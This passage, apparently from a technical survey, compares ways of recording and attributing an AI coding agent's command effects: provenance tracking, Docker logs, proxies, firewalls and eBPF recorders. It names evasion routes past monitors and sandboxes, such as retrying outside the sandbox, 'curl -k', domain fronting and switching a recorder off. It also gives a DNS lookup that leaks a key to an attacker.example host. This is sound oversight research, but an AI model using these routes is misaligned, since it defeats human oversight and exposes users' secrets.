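The second and third rules pass the mark from one process tree to another. If the agent writes a script and cron runs it an hour later, the shell that reads the script gets the mark even though cron started that shell. The fourth rule keeps short-lived helper processes connected to the work they were part of, but it also creates some false links.

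The paper expresses the rules as one equation:

```
τ(t+1) = τ(t) ∨ (τ(t) ⊗ C(t))
```

Here `τ(t)` is a row of zeros and ones with one entry for every process and file, where 1 means marked. `C(t)` is a matrix for the event at time t, with a single 1 in the row of the event's source and the column of its target. A write goes from a process to a file, and a read goes from a file to a process. `⊗` is matrix multiplication with "and" and "or" in place of multiplying and adding, and `∨` is "or". The target therefore becomes marked if the source was marked, and no event removes a mark. In practice, the monitor updates one entry per event and doesn't compute matrices.

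The researchers tested this with a chain they had prepared. An agent started a script that wrote `intermediate_config.tmp`, and `mv` renamed the file to `target_cpuinfo`. A monitoring script that the agent had not started then read the renamed file with `cat` and wrote to `monitor.log`. Agent-Warden connected that last write to the agent. Langfuse, a platform that logs an agent's model calls and tool calls, had no record of the monitoring script.

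Agent-Warden found the full chain in all 120 runs, 30 for each of its two versions on each of two machines. One version keeps the marks in a table indexed by process ID, and the other attaches them to the kernel's records of processes and files. The workload also included a background service that tried to read one of the agent's files about 77 seconds in, long after the agent's main tasks had ended, and Agent-Warden still linked the attempt to the agent.

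The researchers measured overhead by repeating a cycle of process creation, reads, writes and renames 1,000 times. Agent-Warden added 0.2% to 1.1% to the running time on a fast AMD desktop processor and 3.5% on a slower ARM machine. On the AMD machine, the variation between runs was larger than the overhead. The researchers didn't report whether the monitor lost any events.

### False links and missing ones

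The researchers checked that the expected links appeared, but didn't count unwanted ones, and a developer's laptop could have many. For example, if the developer runs `cat src/config.json` in a terminal after `setup.sh` has changed the file, `cat` gets the mark by reading the file, the developer's shell gets it when `cat` exits, and every program the developer then starts in that terminal inherits it.

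Orphaned processes may be a worse problem. *Agent-Warden* acknowledges that the fourth rule can link an orphan to an adopter such as systemd instead of its original parent. Taken literally, the rules would then mark every service that systemd starts afterwards. The process that writes `cache.bin` is one such orphan. An investigator could ignore links from the fourth rule, but would lose some genuine ones too.

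Marks can also be lost. They exist only in memory, so a restart erases them, and the kernel may discard a file's mark when memory runs short. The mark on a weekly cron job's script could easily be gone by the time the job runs.

Agent-Warden doesn't link the deletion of `old.db` to the agent, because its rules cover regular files and `docker` sends its request over a socket. The paper leaves sockets, pipes and network connections to future work. With a simple rule for sockets, the agent's first request would mark `dockerd`, and the mark could then spread to every container the developer started. The monitor's model also has no rule for deletions, only for starting, replacing and ending processes and for reading, writing and renaming files.

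It could still help if the container ran `clean.sh` from the project folder and the agent had written that script. The container's shell would get the mark by reading the marked file, even though the mark had not passed through the socket.

### Logging requests at the socket

Docker can pass each request to a plugin before carrying it out. According to Docker's *Access authorization plugin*, the plugin receives the request's method, address and JSON body, and later the response. For the sample command, the plugin could log `rm /data/old.db`, the shared folder and the container's ID. It could also refuse the request.

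The log might not show who made the request. Docker takes the user's name from the client's TLS certificate, and clients on the local socket normally don't present one, so the agent's containers look the same as the developer's. An administrator could require the agent to connect with its own certificate. Alternatively, the harness could set `DOCKER_HOST` to the address of a small proxy, used only by the agent, that logs and forwards each request. A script could bypass the proxy by connecting to `/var/run/docker.sock` directly.

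The plugin also misses some traffic. Docker doesn't send it gRPC calls, which current versions of `docker build` use, or request bodies that aren't JSON. For `docker exec`, which runs a command in an existing container, the plugin gets only the initial requests. If an agent opened a shell this way and typed commands into it, the log would include the shell but none of the commands. If a container runs a script, the request may contain only the script's name.

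*AppSci-Bench* (2026), a benchmark in which agents build other AI agents, avoids these gaps by giving the agent no access to the Docker socket. The agent writes a container recipe and submits it to a service on the host, which builds and runs it. The service accepts only four kinds of request (health check, submission, deployment and status query), so a log of them can be short and complete. But `setup.sh` would fail there because it expects an ordinary Docker service.

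### Reading Docker's event log

The command `docker events` lists what Docker did with each container. For effect 7, it would show the creation, start, exit and removal of one `alpine` container, along with its exit code. An exit code of 0 means `rm` reported success, which the request alone can't show. The events don't include file changes or identify the caller.

Docker returns only the last 256 events, so a harness should read them as they arrive. While a container exists, `docker inspect` gives its full command and shared folders. But a container run with `--rm` to delete one file may be gone in less than a second, leaving only its image, name and ID.

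### Recording the whole machine

Tetragon and Linux Audit can both record activity in the container's separate process tree, but login user IDs can't connect that activity to the agent, and matching by time can wrongly attribute a deletion made by another container to the agent. With Tetragon, the container ID in `dockerd`'s reply identifies the activity that belongs to the agent's container, so matching by time isn't needed.

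Most other services have no equivalent of the container ID. A database server writes to the same few files for all its clients, so even a complete file log can't show which client dropped a table. The server's own statement log is better evidence, if it is turned on. For a Gradle daemon, the best available clue may be that its writes began just after the agent ran `gradle build`.

### A separate Docker service for the agent

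Docker Sandboxes, a product for running coding agents, puts each agent in a small virtual machine with its own kernel and its own Docker service. According to Docker's *Isolation layers*, the agent has no path to the host's Docker service. A recorder that covers the whole virtual machine can attribute nearly everything that happens there to the agent, including what containers do, without linking the agent's process tree to the Docker service's.

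The sandbox also changes the outcome of the sample command. Unless the developer has shared `/srv/data`, the container can't reach the real `old.db`, so `rm` reports that the file doesn't exist and the script may stop there.

The recorder has to run inside the virtual machine, because the machine's processes aren't visible from the host. The agent has `sudo` rights there, so it could switch the recorder off. Removing the sandbox deletes everything in it, so the harness should copy the log out first. Each sandbox also has to download its own images.

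Some services outside the sandbox can act for the agent. Local MCP servers registered through Docker's gateway run on the host, and any containers they start use the host's Docker service. By default, the sandbox also forwards requests to the developer's `ssh-agent`, so a script could authenticate to a remote server with the developer's key.

If the developer shares the project folder directly, the agent can change the real files, including Git hooks (scripts that Git runs on events such as a commit) and editor tasks that can start when someone opens the project. A recorder in the sandbox would log the change to a hook, but not what the hook does on the host when the developer next commits. Docker advises reviewing such files after every session and notes that hooks don't appear in `git diff`.

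`docker` doesn't work inside Claude Code's own sandbox. Users can exempt commands such as `docker compose`, but Anthropic explains that Claude Code checks the text of the call, so the exemption doesn't cover a script that calls `docker` internally. `./setup.sh` would therefore stay in the sandbox and fail when it calls `docker`. Claude might then retry the whole script outside the sandbox, where nothing would restrict its eight effects. On Linux, the sandbox also needs an optional filter to block sockets, and without it, sandboxed commands may still be able to reach `dockerd`.

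### The sample command

Suppose Agent-Warden runs on the developer's Linux machine with the harness as its starting point, and the script uses the host's Docker service.

| Effect | Agent-Warden's record |
|---|---|
| 1. `src/config.json` overwritten | Write, linked to the agent |
| 2. `notes.md` moved | Rename, linked to the agent |
| 3. Temporary file | Write, if the file received any data |
| 4. Line added to `~/.bashrc` | Write, traceable to npm |
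| 5. `.env` read | Probably the read |
| 6. HTTPS request | Start of the program that sent it, if separate |
| 7. `old.db` deleted | Start of `docker` |
| 8. `cache.bin` written later | Write, linked to the agent |

For `~/.bashrc`, the record can continue after the install. When the developer next opens a terminal, bash reads the marked file and becomes marked too, so the log shows when the added line could first have run.

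## Recording network connections with proxies and connection logs

Snapshots and YoloFS's journal don't record the HTTPS request in the sample command. strace and Linux Audit record the server's address, but not its name or what the script sent. A proxy makes connections on behalf of other programs, so it can log each server's name, the time and the amount of data transferred. A connection log, kept by the kernel or a firewall, records the address and port, and often the process.

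A proxy usually can't identify the process that opened a connection, because it receives only a connection from a local port. A harness could start a separate proxy for each tool call, which would link every log entry to one command.

### An HTTPS request through a proxy

Suppose `setup.sh` uses `curl` to send data to `api.example.com`, and the environment variable `HTTPS_PROXY` contains the proxy's address:

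1. `curl` connects to the proxy and sends the unencrypted line `CONNECT api.example.com:443`.
2. The proxy looks up the server's address, connects to it and tells `curl` that the tunnel is ready.
3. `curl` and the server set up encryption through the tunnel. The server presents a certificate for its name, and `curl` checks that an authority it trusts has signed it.
4. `curl` sends its request, and the proxy passes encrypted bytes in both directions until one side closes the connection.

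The proxy can log the host name, the port, the times and the number of bytes each way. It can't log the path, the contents or the method, such as GET for fetching data or POST for sending it. *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a "limited" mode in OpenAI's Codex that allows only methods meant for fetching, but the proxy can't detect which method a program uses inside an encrypted tunnel.

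The hostname in a proxy log may not be the site the program contacted, because the program supplies that name. Anthropic warns about domain fronting, in which a program asks the proxy for an approved host but addresses a different site inside the encrypted request. This can work when the same content delivery network serves both sites. The log would then contain only the approved name.

A proxy that decrypts traffic sits between `curl` and the server. It generates its own certificate for `api.example.com`, presents it to `curl`, and opens a second encrypted connection to the real server. It can then read and log each request it forwards, including any key from `.env` that the request contains.

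### What decryption costs and breaks

`curl` accepts the generated certificate only if it trusts the proxy's signing authority, and programs don't all use the same list of trusted authorities. Claude Code uses both its own list and the operating system's, but Anthropic notes that a copy installed through npm needs Node.js 22.15 or later to read the system's. For Node.js programs, *Sandboxing agentic coding tools is a networking problem*, by the security company Formal, recommends setting `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` to the proxy's certificate. Java normally has its own list, and so does each container image.

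Some programs fail even then, because they accept only one particular certificate for their service. On macOS, tools written in Go, such as GitHub's `gh`, may fail to verify certificates inside Claude Code's sandbox. To fix this for users with a decrypting proxy, Anthropic provides a setting called `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation`. An agent that gets certificate errors might try `curl -k`, which turns off certificate verification.

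The log becomes sensitive too, since it can contain passwords and private source code. Anyone who steals the proxy's signing key can impersonate any website to the machines that trust it.

### Making the proxy unavoidable

Setting `HTTPS_PROXY` doesn't force programs to use the proxy. `curl`, npm and Git over HTTPS read the variable, but plain `ssh` and most database drivers ignore it, and a script can unset it. On an ordinary machine, programs that don't use the proxy connect directly and leave no entry in its log.

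On Linux, a network namespace prevents programs from bypassing the proxy. It gives a group of processes their own network interfaces, which the harness leaves unconnected to the outside. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, processes in Claude Code's sandbox can reach the network only through a local socket that leads to a proxy outside the namespace. A program that ignores the proxy settings fails with an error such as "Network is unreachable". On macOS, a sandbox rule blocks connections to anything except the proxy.

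The log then covers all the traffic that gets out, but some legitimate tools stop working. A test suite that connects to a remote database, for example, fails even if the user has approved the database's host.

### Name lookups and traffic that isn't HTTP

Without a proxy, a program first looks up the address of `api.example.com` through a name server. A connection log then contains only an address such as 203.0.113.10, which may belong to a hosting provider with thousands of customers. The log also needs to include the lookups to help identify the host.

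A DNS lookup can leak data even if no connection follows. If a script looks up `k3y-from-env.attacker.example`, the request normally reaches the attacker's name server with the secret in the name. A closed network namespace whose only way out is a proxy prevents this, because the proxy looks up names itself, and only after checking the host.

Firewalls that filter by address have to look up the addresses of approved domain names in advance. Depot, which rents out build machines, saves these addresses in the machine's `/etc/hosts` file, according to its *Use egress filters for GitHub Actions runners*. Depot adds that any process with root access can change the filter's rules.

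A program can send UDP packets, which DNS lookups and HTTP/3 use, through the `sendto` system call without calling `connect`. The Audit rule for `connect` shown earlier would miss these packets. Claude Code's sandbox blocks all outgoing UDP traffic and the packets that `ping` sends.

### The Claude Code sandbox

Claude Code's sandbox is off by default. Once it is on, the list of approved domains starts empty, and Claude Code asks the user about each new host. The only connections the built-in proxy is documented to record are those it refuses. Claude Code names the refused host in the command's result, so the name lasts as long as the session's transcript. If the user approves a host permanently, the approval also stays in a settings file, but that entry doesn't show when or how often a command used the host.

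In auto mode, where a second model reviews actions in place of the user, Claude lists the hosts that a command needs as part of the tool call. The transcript then contains the hosts Claude expected the command to need, which may differ from those it contacted. If a command tries another host, Claude Code blocks the connection, and Claude runs the command again with the host added. Rerunning `./setup.sh` could repeat whatever the script had already done, and `notes.md` may no longer be there to move.

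For a full log, Anthropic tells users to replace Claude Code's built-in proxy with their own. Claude Code's approved domains and prompts then no longer apply to traffic sent to the user's proxy. The built-in proxy uses two ports, and if the user replaces only one, commands can still connect through the other without appearing in the new log.

Traffic can also bypass the sandbox, because Claude Code's own web tools, hooks and local MCP servers run outside it. If the sandbox can't start, for instance because a package is missing, Claude Code runs commands without it by default.

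### The firewall of GitHub's Copilot agent

GitHub's cloud version of Copilot works on a temporary machine in GitHub Actions, the company's automated build service. A firewall there allows a recommended list of hosts, including package registries, container registries and certificate authorities. When the firewall blocks a request, Copilot adds a warning to the pull request (the proposed change that a person reviews) with the address and the command that tried to reach it, so a reviewer is likely to see it.

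Requests to approved hosts produce no warning, so a script that uploaded a key to one would not be flagged. In July 2026, GitHub was also testing a separate log of all outbound traffic from Actions runs.

A run's logs don't last as long as the pull request. GitHub keeps them for 90 days by default, and since October 2026 it has applied the same limit to the list of runs, which it used to keep for more than 400 days, according to GitHub's *Actions retention will cover checks, workflow runs, and statuses* (2026).

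The firewall covers only processes that the agent starts with its Bash tool, so it doesn't cover MCP servers or the setup steps that a project configures to run before the agent begins. A project's `setup.sh` would be a natural setup step, and the firewall wouldn't cover its HTTPS request there. GitHub also warns that sophisticated attacks may get around the firewall.

### Harden-Runner on build machines

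Harden-Runner, from the security company StepSecurity, monitors build machines such as those of GitHub Actions. According to StepSecurity's *Harden-Runner*, the tool sends the company the names that programs looked up, the addresses and ports they contacted, the process responsible and the time. It links each event to a build step. On Linux it also records the method, host and path of HTTPS requests, which it reads with eBPF, so it needs no certificate.

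These details matter when an attacker hides a theft among ordinary requests to GitHub, as in the Nx attack. StepSecurity's *Monitor Outbound HTTPS Requests from GitHub Actions Runners* gives the example of an attacker who creates a new issue through GitHub's API. The method and path would reveal this, while a log of host names would show only a normal connection to GitHub.

StepSecurity doesn't collect file contents or the values of environment variables, but it gives paying customers process events with full arguments, so a key that a script passes on the command line could end up in the log. The company's description of its data handling gives no retention period, but customers can export events to their own storage. The free version works only for public repositories, and anyone can view its logs.

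Harden-Runner can't read HTTPS requests on macOS or Windows and records no file writes on Windows. Before version 2.14.2, programs could evade the free version's connection log by sending data with `sendto` and two similar calls, according to the National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2026-25598 Detail*.

### The axios attack in a connection log

Harden-Runner's log revealed the attack on axios, in which a malicious package ran an install script and then hid it. The script downloaded a program that gave the attackers remote control, according to Sophos' *Axios npm package compromised to deploy malware*.

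During a routine build of Backstage, an open-source framework for developer websites, Harden-Runner recorded a connection to the attackers' server on port 8000. It flagged the connection because no earlier run of that build had contacted the server. According to StepSecurity, the Backstage team said the build ran in a sandbox and the install did not affect the project.

In StepSecurity's test, the connection came 1.1 seconds after `npm install` started, according to Techzine's *Axios npm package compromised, posing a new supply chain threat*. A harness that reviewed the log only after the command finished would have been too late to stop the connection.

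The account comes from the company that sells the tool, but the build's log is public, so anyone can check it. The method also suits builds better than agents. A build normally contacts the same servers on every run, so an unfamiliar server stands out. StepSecurity's *Workflow Runs* warns that jobs with unpredictable traffic cause frequent false alarms. An agent that reads documentation and tries new packages would probably produce such traffic.

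### Deciding what to revoke or repair

A user can't undo a request, so the log's main use after an incident is to work out what to replace or repair. The first task is to find the affected machines. StepSecurity describes customers who used the lists of usual destinations to check whether an attack had succeeded. The absence of the attacker's address from a log suggests that a machine wasn't affected only if the log covered that machine, the time of the attack and the kind of traffic involved.

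The amount of data sent helps rule out a large theft. A process that sent 2 KB didn't upload the whole repository, but 2 KB is enough for dozens of access keys.

A connection log doesn't show which credentials a process sent. Unless a decrypting proxy recorded the contents, the user has to assume that the process leaked every credential it could read. In the axios case, the advice was to replace npm tokens, cloud keys, SSH keys and build-system secrets. A complete log of file reads could shorten that list.

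Some requests change something on the server, for example by creating a repository or deleting a cloud database. The request's method and path identify what to delete or restore. The script's output is weaker evidence, because a server may carry out a request even if the reply never arrives and the script reports an error.

If the user marks a credential for masking, Claude Code can also give sandboxed commands a placeholder that is useless if leaked. The proxy inserts the real value only in requests to approved hosts. On Linux, this works for files such as `.env`, but on macOS the command can't read the file at all. Masking needs the experimental setting that makes the proxy decrypt traffic. Unless the user names the hosts that may receive each key, the proxy inserts it in requests to every approved host, including one where an attacker may have an account.

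### Answering with placeholders

Wu and colleagues suggest a proxy for Caper's trial runs that would answer requests with placeholders, so nothing would leave the machine. Caper's reports already mark replies from simulated services, so the approver can tell them from real ones.

Placeholder replies work best for requests whose replies don't matter, such as usage statistics. An npm download would fail because the placeholder wouldn't match the hash in the lock file. A script that logs in to a service wouldn't get a valid token, so its later steps would fail or run differently.

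Malware would also behave differently. The axios install script would contact its server and receive a placeholder instead of the second program. The approver would learn about the connection, but not what the second program does.

Caper keeps the result of the trial run instead of running an approved command again, which creates a harder problem. If the approver allows a deployment, the real server never receives it. A script that creates a cloud server and saves its ID would leave a made-up ID in the project. The harness would have to either run the command again without a trial or send the recorded requests afterwards, which may fail if a later request depends on an earlier reply.

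A proxy could let through requests that fetch data and hold back only those that send it, as Codex's limited mode does. npm could then download packages, but a script could still leak a stolen key by putting it in the URL of a GET request.

### The sample command

Only three of the eight effects involve the internet: `npm install` downloads packages, the script sends its HTTPS request, and `dockerd` downloads the `alpine` image if the machine doesn't have it. For the two proxy logs, we assume the script runs without a sandbox and that `curl` and npm use the proxy. The connection log follows the agent's processes. Harden-Runner here means the paid version running on a Linux build machine.

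| Record | npm's downloads | HTTPS request | Image download |
|---|---|---|---|
| Proxy without decryption | Registry's name, time, volume | Server's name, time, volume | Nothing |
| Proxy with decryption | Each package's address | Method, path and contents | Nothing |
| Connection log | Address, port, process | Address, port, process | Nothing |
| Claude Code sandbox | Host, if refused | Host, if refused | `docker` fails |
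| Copilot firewall | Nothing, because the registry is approved | Address and command, if blocked | Nothing |
| Harden-Runner | Names, addresses, ports, process | Name, address, port, process, method and path | Name, address, port, process |

The image download is missing from the proxy logs because `dockerd` doesn't inherit the script's environment variables.

Harden-Runner also records file writes in the project folder, so its log would include `src/config.json` but not the line in `~/.bashrc`. It would include `cache.bin` only if the build is still running when that file is written. None of these records shows that the script read `.env`, but the decrypting proxy would show any key from it that the script sent in readable form.

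## Cost, lost events and coverage compared

No recorder described so far captures all eight effects of `./setup.sh` and attributes each one to the agent. In the table below, "Yes" means that the record shows the effect and connects it to the agent, "Unlinked" means that it shows the effect but not the connection, and "No" means that the effect is missing. A record that a program such as `mv`, `curl` or `docker` started doesn't count as showing the effect, because the program can still fail.

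Each tool uses the settings given in its own section. The temporary file receives some data, and the background process writes `cache.bin` after the shell has exited but before the agent's next command.

| Record | 1. `config.json` | 2. Move | 3. Temporary file | 4. `~/.bashrc` | 5. `.env` read | 6. HTTPS | 7. `old.db` | 8. `cache.bin` |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Transcript or Claude Code checkpoint | No | No | No | No | No | No | No | No |
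| OpenCode's shadow repository | Unlinked | Unlinked | No | No | No | No | No | No |
| strace | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | Yes |
| Linux Audit | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Unlinked | Yes |
| inotify | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | No | Unlinked | Unlinked |
| fanotify | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | No | Unlinked | Unlinked |
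| Tetragon with the write policy | Yes | No | Yes | Yes | No | No | No | Yes |
| AgentSight | Yes | No | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | Yes |
| NTFS change journal or FSEvents | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | Unlinked | No | No | Unlinked | Unlinked |
| ETW | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Unlinked | Yes |
| Sysmon | Yes | No | Yes | No | No | Yes | Unlinked | Yes |
| Endpoint Security through `eslogger` | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | Unlinked | Yes |
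| `try` | Yes | Yes | No | Yes | No | No | No | No |
| ZFS, Btrfs or APFS snapshot | Unlinked | Unlinked | No | Unlinked | No | No | Unlinked | No |
| YoloFS | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | No | No | Yes |
| Agent-Warden | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | No | Yes |
| Proxy | No | No | No | No | No | Unlinked | No | No |
| Connection log by process | No | No | No | No | No | Yes | No | No |

The column for `old.db` has no "Yes" because a Docker container deletes the file outside the agent's process tree and outside any overlay.

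None of the four methods that keep old contents for a whole command (shadow repositories, `try`, snapshots and YoloFS) records the read of `.env` or the HTTPS request.

fanotify gets "Unlinked" although it supplies a process ID with every event, because the ID alone doesn't lead back to the agent. Sysmon misses the line in `~/.bashrc` because it has no event for appending to a file. If the script had rewritten the whole file, Sysmon would have reported it. Tetragon's gaps for the move, the read and the request come from the sample policy, which covers only writes.

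### What eBPF recording costs

In a study from August 2026, Houssel and colleagues rated five ways of capturing kernel activity on portability, efficiency, visibility, safety and robustness against attackers. Only eBPF rated well on efficiency, visibility and safety all at once. Kernel modules match it on efficiency and visibility, but each build works with only one kernel version, and a faulty module can crash the machine. Facilities built into the kernel, such as Audit, are safe but less efficient. Snapshots add little overhead but show only file changes, and `ptrace` rated poorly on most criteria. None of the five received the top rating for robustness.

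The researchers then measured eBPF programs on a 24-core Linux machine with three workloads in Docker containers:

- **Network:** 50,000 HTTP connections to a local web server.
- **File:** writing 50,000 files of 512 KB each.
- **Process:** running the `echo` program 50,000 times in a row.

The table gives the extra processor time compared with an untraced run, averaged over ten runs.

| Program type | Attachment | Network | File | Process |
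|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fentry | System-call entry | 0.76% | 8.12% | 1.15% |
| Tracepoint | System-call entry | 1.43% | 8.63% | 1.22% |
| Kprobe | System-call entry | 1.66% | 9.10% | 1.30% |
| Fentry and fexit | Security check, entry and exit | 1.22% | 10.01% | 2.04% |
| Kprobe | Security check, entry and exit | 1.40% | 12.99% | 2.10% |
| LSM | Security hook | 0.89% | 7.27% | 1.13% |

The programs in the first three rows have low overhead partly because they don't capture whether the kernel allowed the operation. Those in the last three rows do, and the LSM program has the lowest overhead among them.

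The file workload has the highest overhead for every type. A program that watches system calls has to inspect 100,000 file opens to find the 50,000 that create a file, because the workload opens each file again to read it. The security hook runs only when a process creates a file.

For filtering, Houssel and colleagues ran two copies of each container and traced only one, much as an agent's container might run beside the developer's own. These are the LSM program's results:

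| Filter | Network | File | Process |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kernel runs the program only for the chosen container | 0.69% | 7.89% | 0.45% |
| Program checks the container itself | 0.85% | 8.55% | 0.85% |
| Recorder sorts the events afterwards | 1.65% | 9.55% | 1.66% |

Sorting events afterwards also doubles the number that the kernel has to pass on, which puts more strain on the buffer.

### Events that never reach the log

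The coverage table assumes that no recorder loses events. Houssel and colleagues tested complete recording systems on the same workloads and calculated the loss from one kind of event whose true number they knew:

```
log loss = (1 − traced / expected) × 100
```

The process workload should produce 50,000 process creations. If the log contains 1,500 of them, the loss is (1 − 1,500 / 50,000) × 100 = 97%. Because the formula compares the final log with the true count, it includes losses anywhere between the kernel and the disk but doesn't show where they happened.

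eAudit, an eBPF recorder that monitors 81 system calls, lost nothing in any workload. It added 5.9% in the network workload and 12% in the file workload. It encodes events compactly, gives each processor core its own buffer and treats some system calls as more important than others. It also writes a plain stream of events and leaves the analysis for later.

The other four systems build provenance graphs, which link processes to the files and connections they used. Most of them lost 90% to 100% of events in most workloads. SPADE, which gets its events from Linux Audit, lost 91% to 99% and added 13.4% overhead in the process workload. CamFlow, which needs a modified kernel, added 55% overhead in the network workload and 45% in the file workload. It lost about 95% of events in those two workloads but none in the process workload. ConProv, which monitors only nine points in the kernel, lost more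 than 97%.

eAudit's design would suit an agent harness, because the harness could store the raw stream during a command and work out the process tree afterwards. But the stream holds 4.1 million links between processes and files for the process workload alone, so somebody still has to write the program that reduces it to a readable record.

The study's appendix covers general-purpose tools, including Sysdig, Tracee and Tetragon. These tools traced far more kinds of events, and Houssel and colleagues report large logs and considerable event loss. Those results don't apply to a Tetragon policy that filters for one harness's file writes, because it sends far fewer events to the buffer.

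Other test conditions also limit how far the results apply to agents. Each provenance system ran on Fedora 35, a Linux release from 2021, because the modified kernels support no other distribution. The researchers kept the default settings, and SPADE might have lost fewer events with a longer queue. The workloads are also much denser than ordinary agent work. King and colleagues traced 4,047 agent sessions and recorded an average of about 3,500 kernel events per session. A large `npm install` is closer to the file workload, so heavy losses are most likely during commands like this, which can run a stranger's code.

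Recorders that check the machine at intervals lose events even when little is happening. *ExecWeave* measured this with processes of known length:

| Process lived for about | Time between checks | Runs in which the recorder saw it |
|---|---|---|
| 16 ms | 20 ms | 18 of 30 |
| 16 ms | 500 ms | 0 of 30 |
| 61 ms | 100 ms | 21 of 30 |
| 263 ms | 500 ms | 13 of 30 |

A lost process can also lead to a wrong attribution. ExecWeave links a tool call to a process only if exactly one observed process fits. In a test where the true process was missing and one similar process remained, ExecWeave could link the call to the wrong process.

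### Why the published overheads can't be ranked

Dong and colleagues report 821% for Linux Audit, which is a worst case for running time. SPADE also uses Audit, but its 13.4% figure is for processor time in a single test in which most events never reached the log.

The percentage overhead also depends on how long the test runs. The same version of ExecWeave added 408.8% to a job of about 0.09 seconds and 62.3% to one of about 4.1 seconds. *NovaFabric* (2026), which describes a recorder for complete agent runs, reports an overhead of 169 milliseconds for a Python command that does nothing, using a faster way of loading the recorder. For full capture, it reports a fixed overhead of 4.56 seconds, plus about half a millisecond for each intercepted call. That fixed overhead is 456% of a one-second command but about 0.8% of a ten-minute session.

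Timing a whole agent session can hide how much a recorder slows down shell commands. When Zheng and colleagues tested AgentSight, one task took 128 seconds without it, and Claude Code probably spent much of that time waiting for the model. If shell commands took five of those seconds and a recorder doubled that, the session would take only 3.9% longer.

| System | Reported cost | What the test timed |
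|---|---|---|
| AgentSight | 2.9% on average | Whole agent tasks, including the model's replies |
| Agent-Warden | 0.2% to 3.5% | A repeated cycle of process and file operations |
| Caper | About 0.5 s per allowed command | Short commands without network access |
| ExecWeave | 62.3% to 408.8% | Fixed file and process work without a model |
| NovaFabric | 4.56 s per run, plus about 0.5 ms per call | Workloads of different lengths |
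| `try` | 10% to 90% | Five scripts generated by ChatGPT |
| YoloFS | 3.5 s at the end of the session | Development work on the Linux kernel |

A fair ranking would require running the same commands, including a large `npm install`, on one machine and reporting lost events alongside running time. A recorder may have low overhead because it drops events and so avoids the work of handling them.

### Pairs that close each other's gaps

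A staged file system and a log of processes and connections complement each other. If `./setup.sh` ran in YoloFS under strace, the record would include every effect except the deletion of `old.db`. YoloFS would let the user undo the file changes, and strace would record the read of `.env`, the HTTPS request and the chain of processes from npm to `~/.bashrc`.

Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, describe a system that joins three such mechanisms around each command:

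1. Tether starts the command in a disposable OverlayFS layer, as `try` does, with strace attached.
2. A local proxy holds each outgoing request and records its destination and, where possible, its address, headers and contents.
3. Tether turns the trace and the proxy's log into a short list of actions, such as "copy" and "upload", and checks them against a written policy.
4. If the policy allows everything, Tether forwards the requests and applies the file changes. Otherwise it discards both.

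The combination also links events that the separate logs would leave unconnected. Tether keeps a list of the files each process has read and passes it to downstream processes. If the shell reads `.env` and then starts `curl`, Tether treats `curl`'s request as an upload of `.env`. The script may have sent something unrelated, but Sistla and colleagues accept some false alarms to avoid missing a leak.

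Tether doesn't solve the `old.db` case. It can detect and block contact with a background service or a database, but can't trace what the service does. The process that writes `cache.bin` is also difficult to handle. Tether pauses background processes that outlive the shell, but its strace ends with the command, so a policy may have to block them altogether.

Capturing the deletion of `old.db` requires a different pair of tools, strace and Tetragon, with their logs linked by container ID. With an added probe for deletions, Tetragon would also show whether the file disappeared. Together, the two logs would supply the missing "Yes". Restoring the file also requires a snapshot of `/srv/data`, which someone must have set up beforehand.

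Snapshots become more practical if an event log is used to decide when to take them. Zhong and colleagues mention a system called Crab that uses eBPF to identify a command's effects and saves a ZFS checkpoint only where needed. *Planarian* (2026) pairs ZFS snapshots with CRIU, a program that saves running processes so that they can resume later, and returns a container's processes to their earlier state along with its files. If a user restores only the files after `./setup.sh`, the background process keeps running and writes `cache.bin` into the restored project.

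Adding recorders helps little if they all miss the same information. *Reasoning Provenance for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026) combines a proxy for MCP tools, a handler that the shell runs before each command, and a file watcher, then compares their records with the agent's own account. This can expose an agent that misreports its actions. But for `./setup.sh`, the shell handler would normally record only one command, because a script started as a separate program doesn't inherit the handler. The file watcher doesn't identify processes, so most of the file changes would not be linked to the commands that made them.

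The transcript has little value as a record of effects, but it complements a kernel log for detecting attacks on the agent. King and colleagues trained detectors on system-call traces, on transcripts and tool descriptions, and on both. The combination generally did best, because each source helped detect some kinds of attack that were hard to detect from the other. Even on the kernel measurements that best separated malicious sessions from harmless ones, typical sessions of both kinds looked the same, and only the extremes differed.

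### Effects that no pair covers

Even a complete record of activity on the developer's machine doesn't show what happens on remote systems. If the HTTPS request in `setup.sh` deletes a cloud database, a decrypting proxy can record the request and the reply, but only the provider's logs can confirm the deletion. *ExecWeave* describes the same limit for remote MCP servers, whose work can't be observed from the machine that calls them.

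Local services, such as a shared database server, can also hide which program caused a change. A process can use a key agent such as `ssh-agent` without reading any file, as *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) points out, so a script may have used the developer's key even if the log shows no access to `~/.ssh`.

Delayed effects are another gap in coverage. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* warns that startup files and hooks written during a session can run later, outside the sandbox. The line in `~/.bashrc` may run days after the harness has closed its log, so recording its effects requires a tool that keeps running between sessions, such as Agent-Warden.

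A harness can also prevent some effects that it can't record or reverse. *NaSh* (2025), a design for a shell that takes instructions in ordinary language, would keep the old contents of changed files in an undo log and run scripts in separate network and process namespaces. This isolation would stop a script from contacting an outside server or interfering with other programs, but it would also make `npm install` fail.
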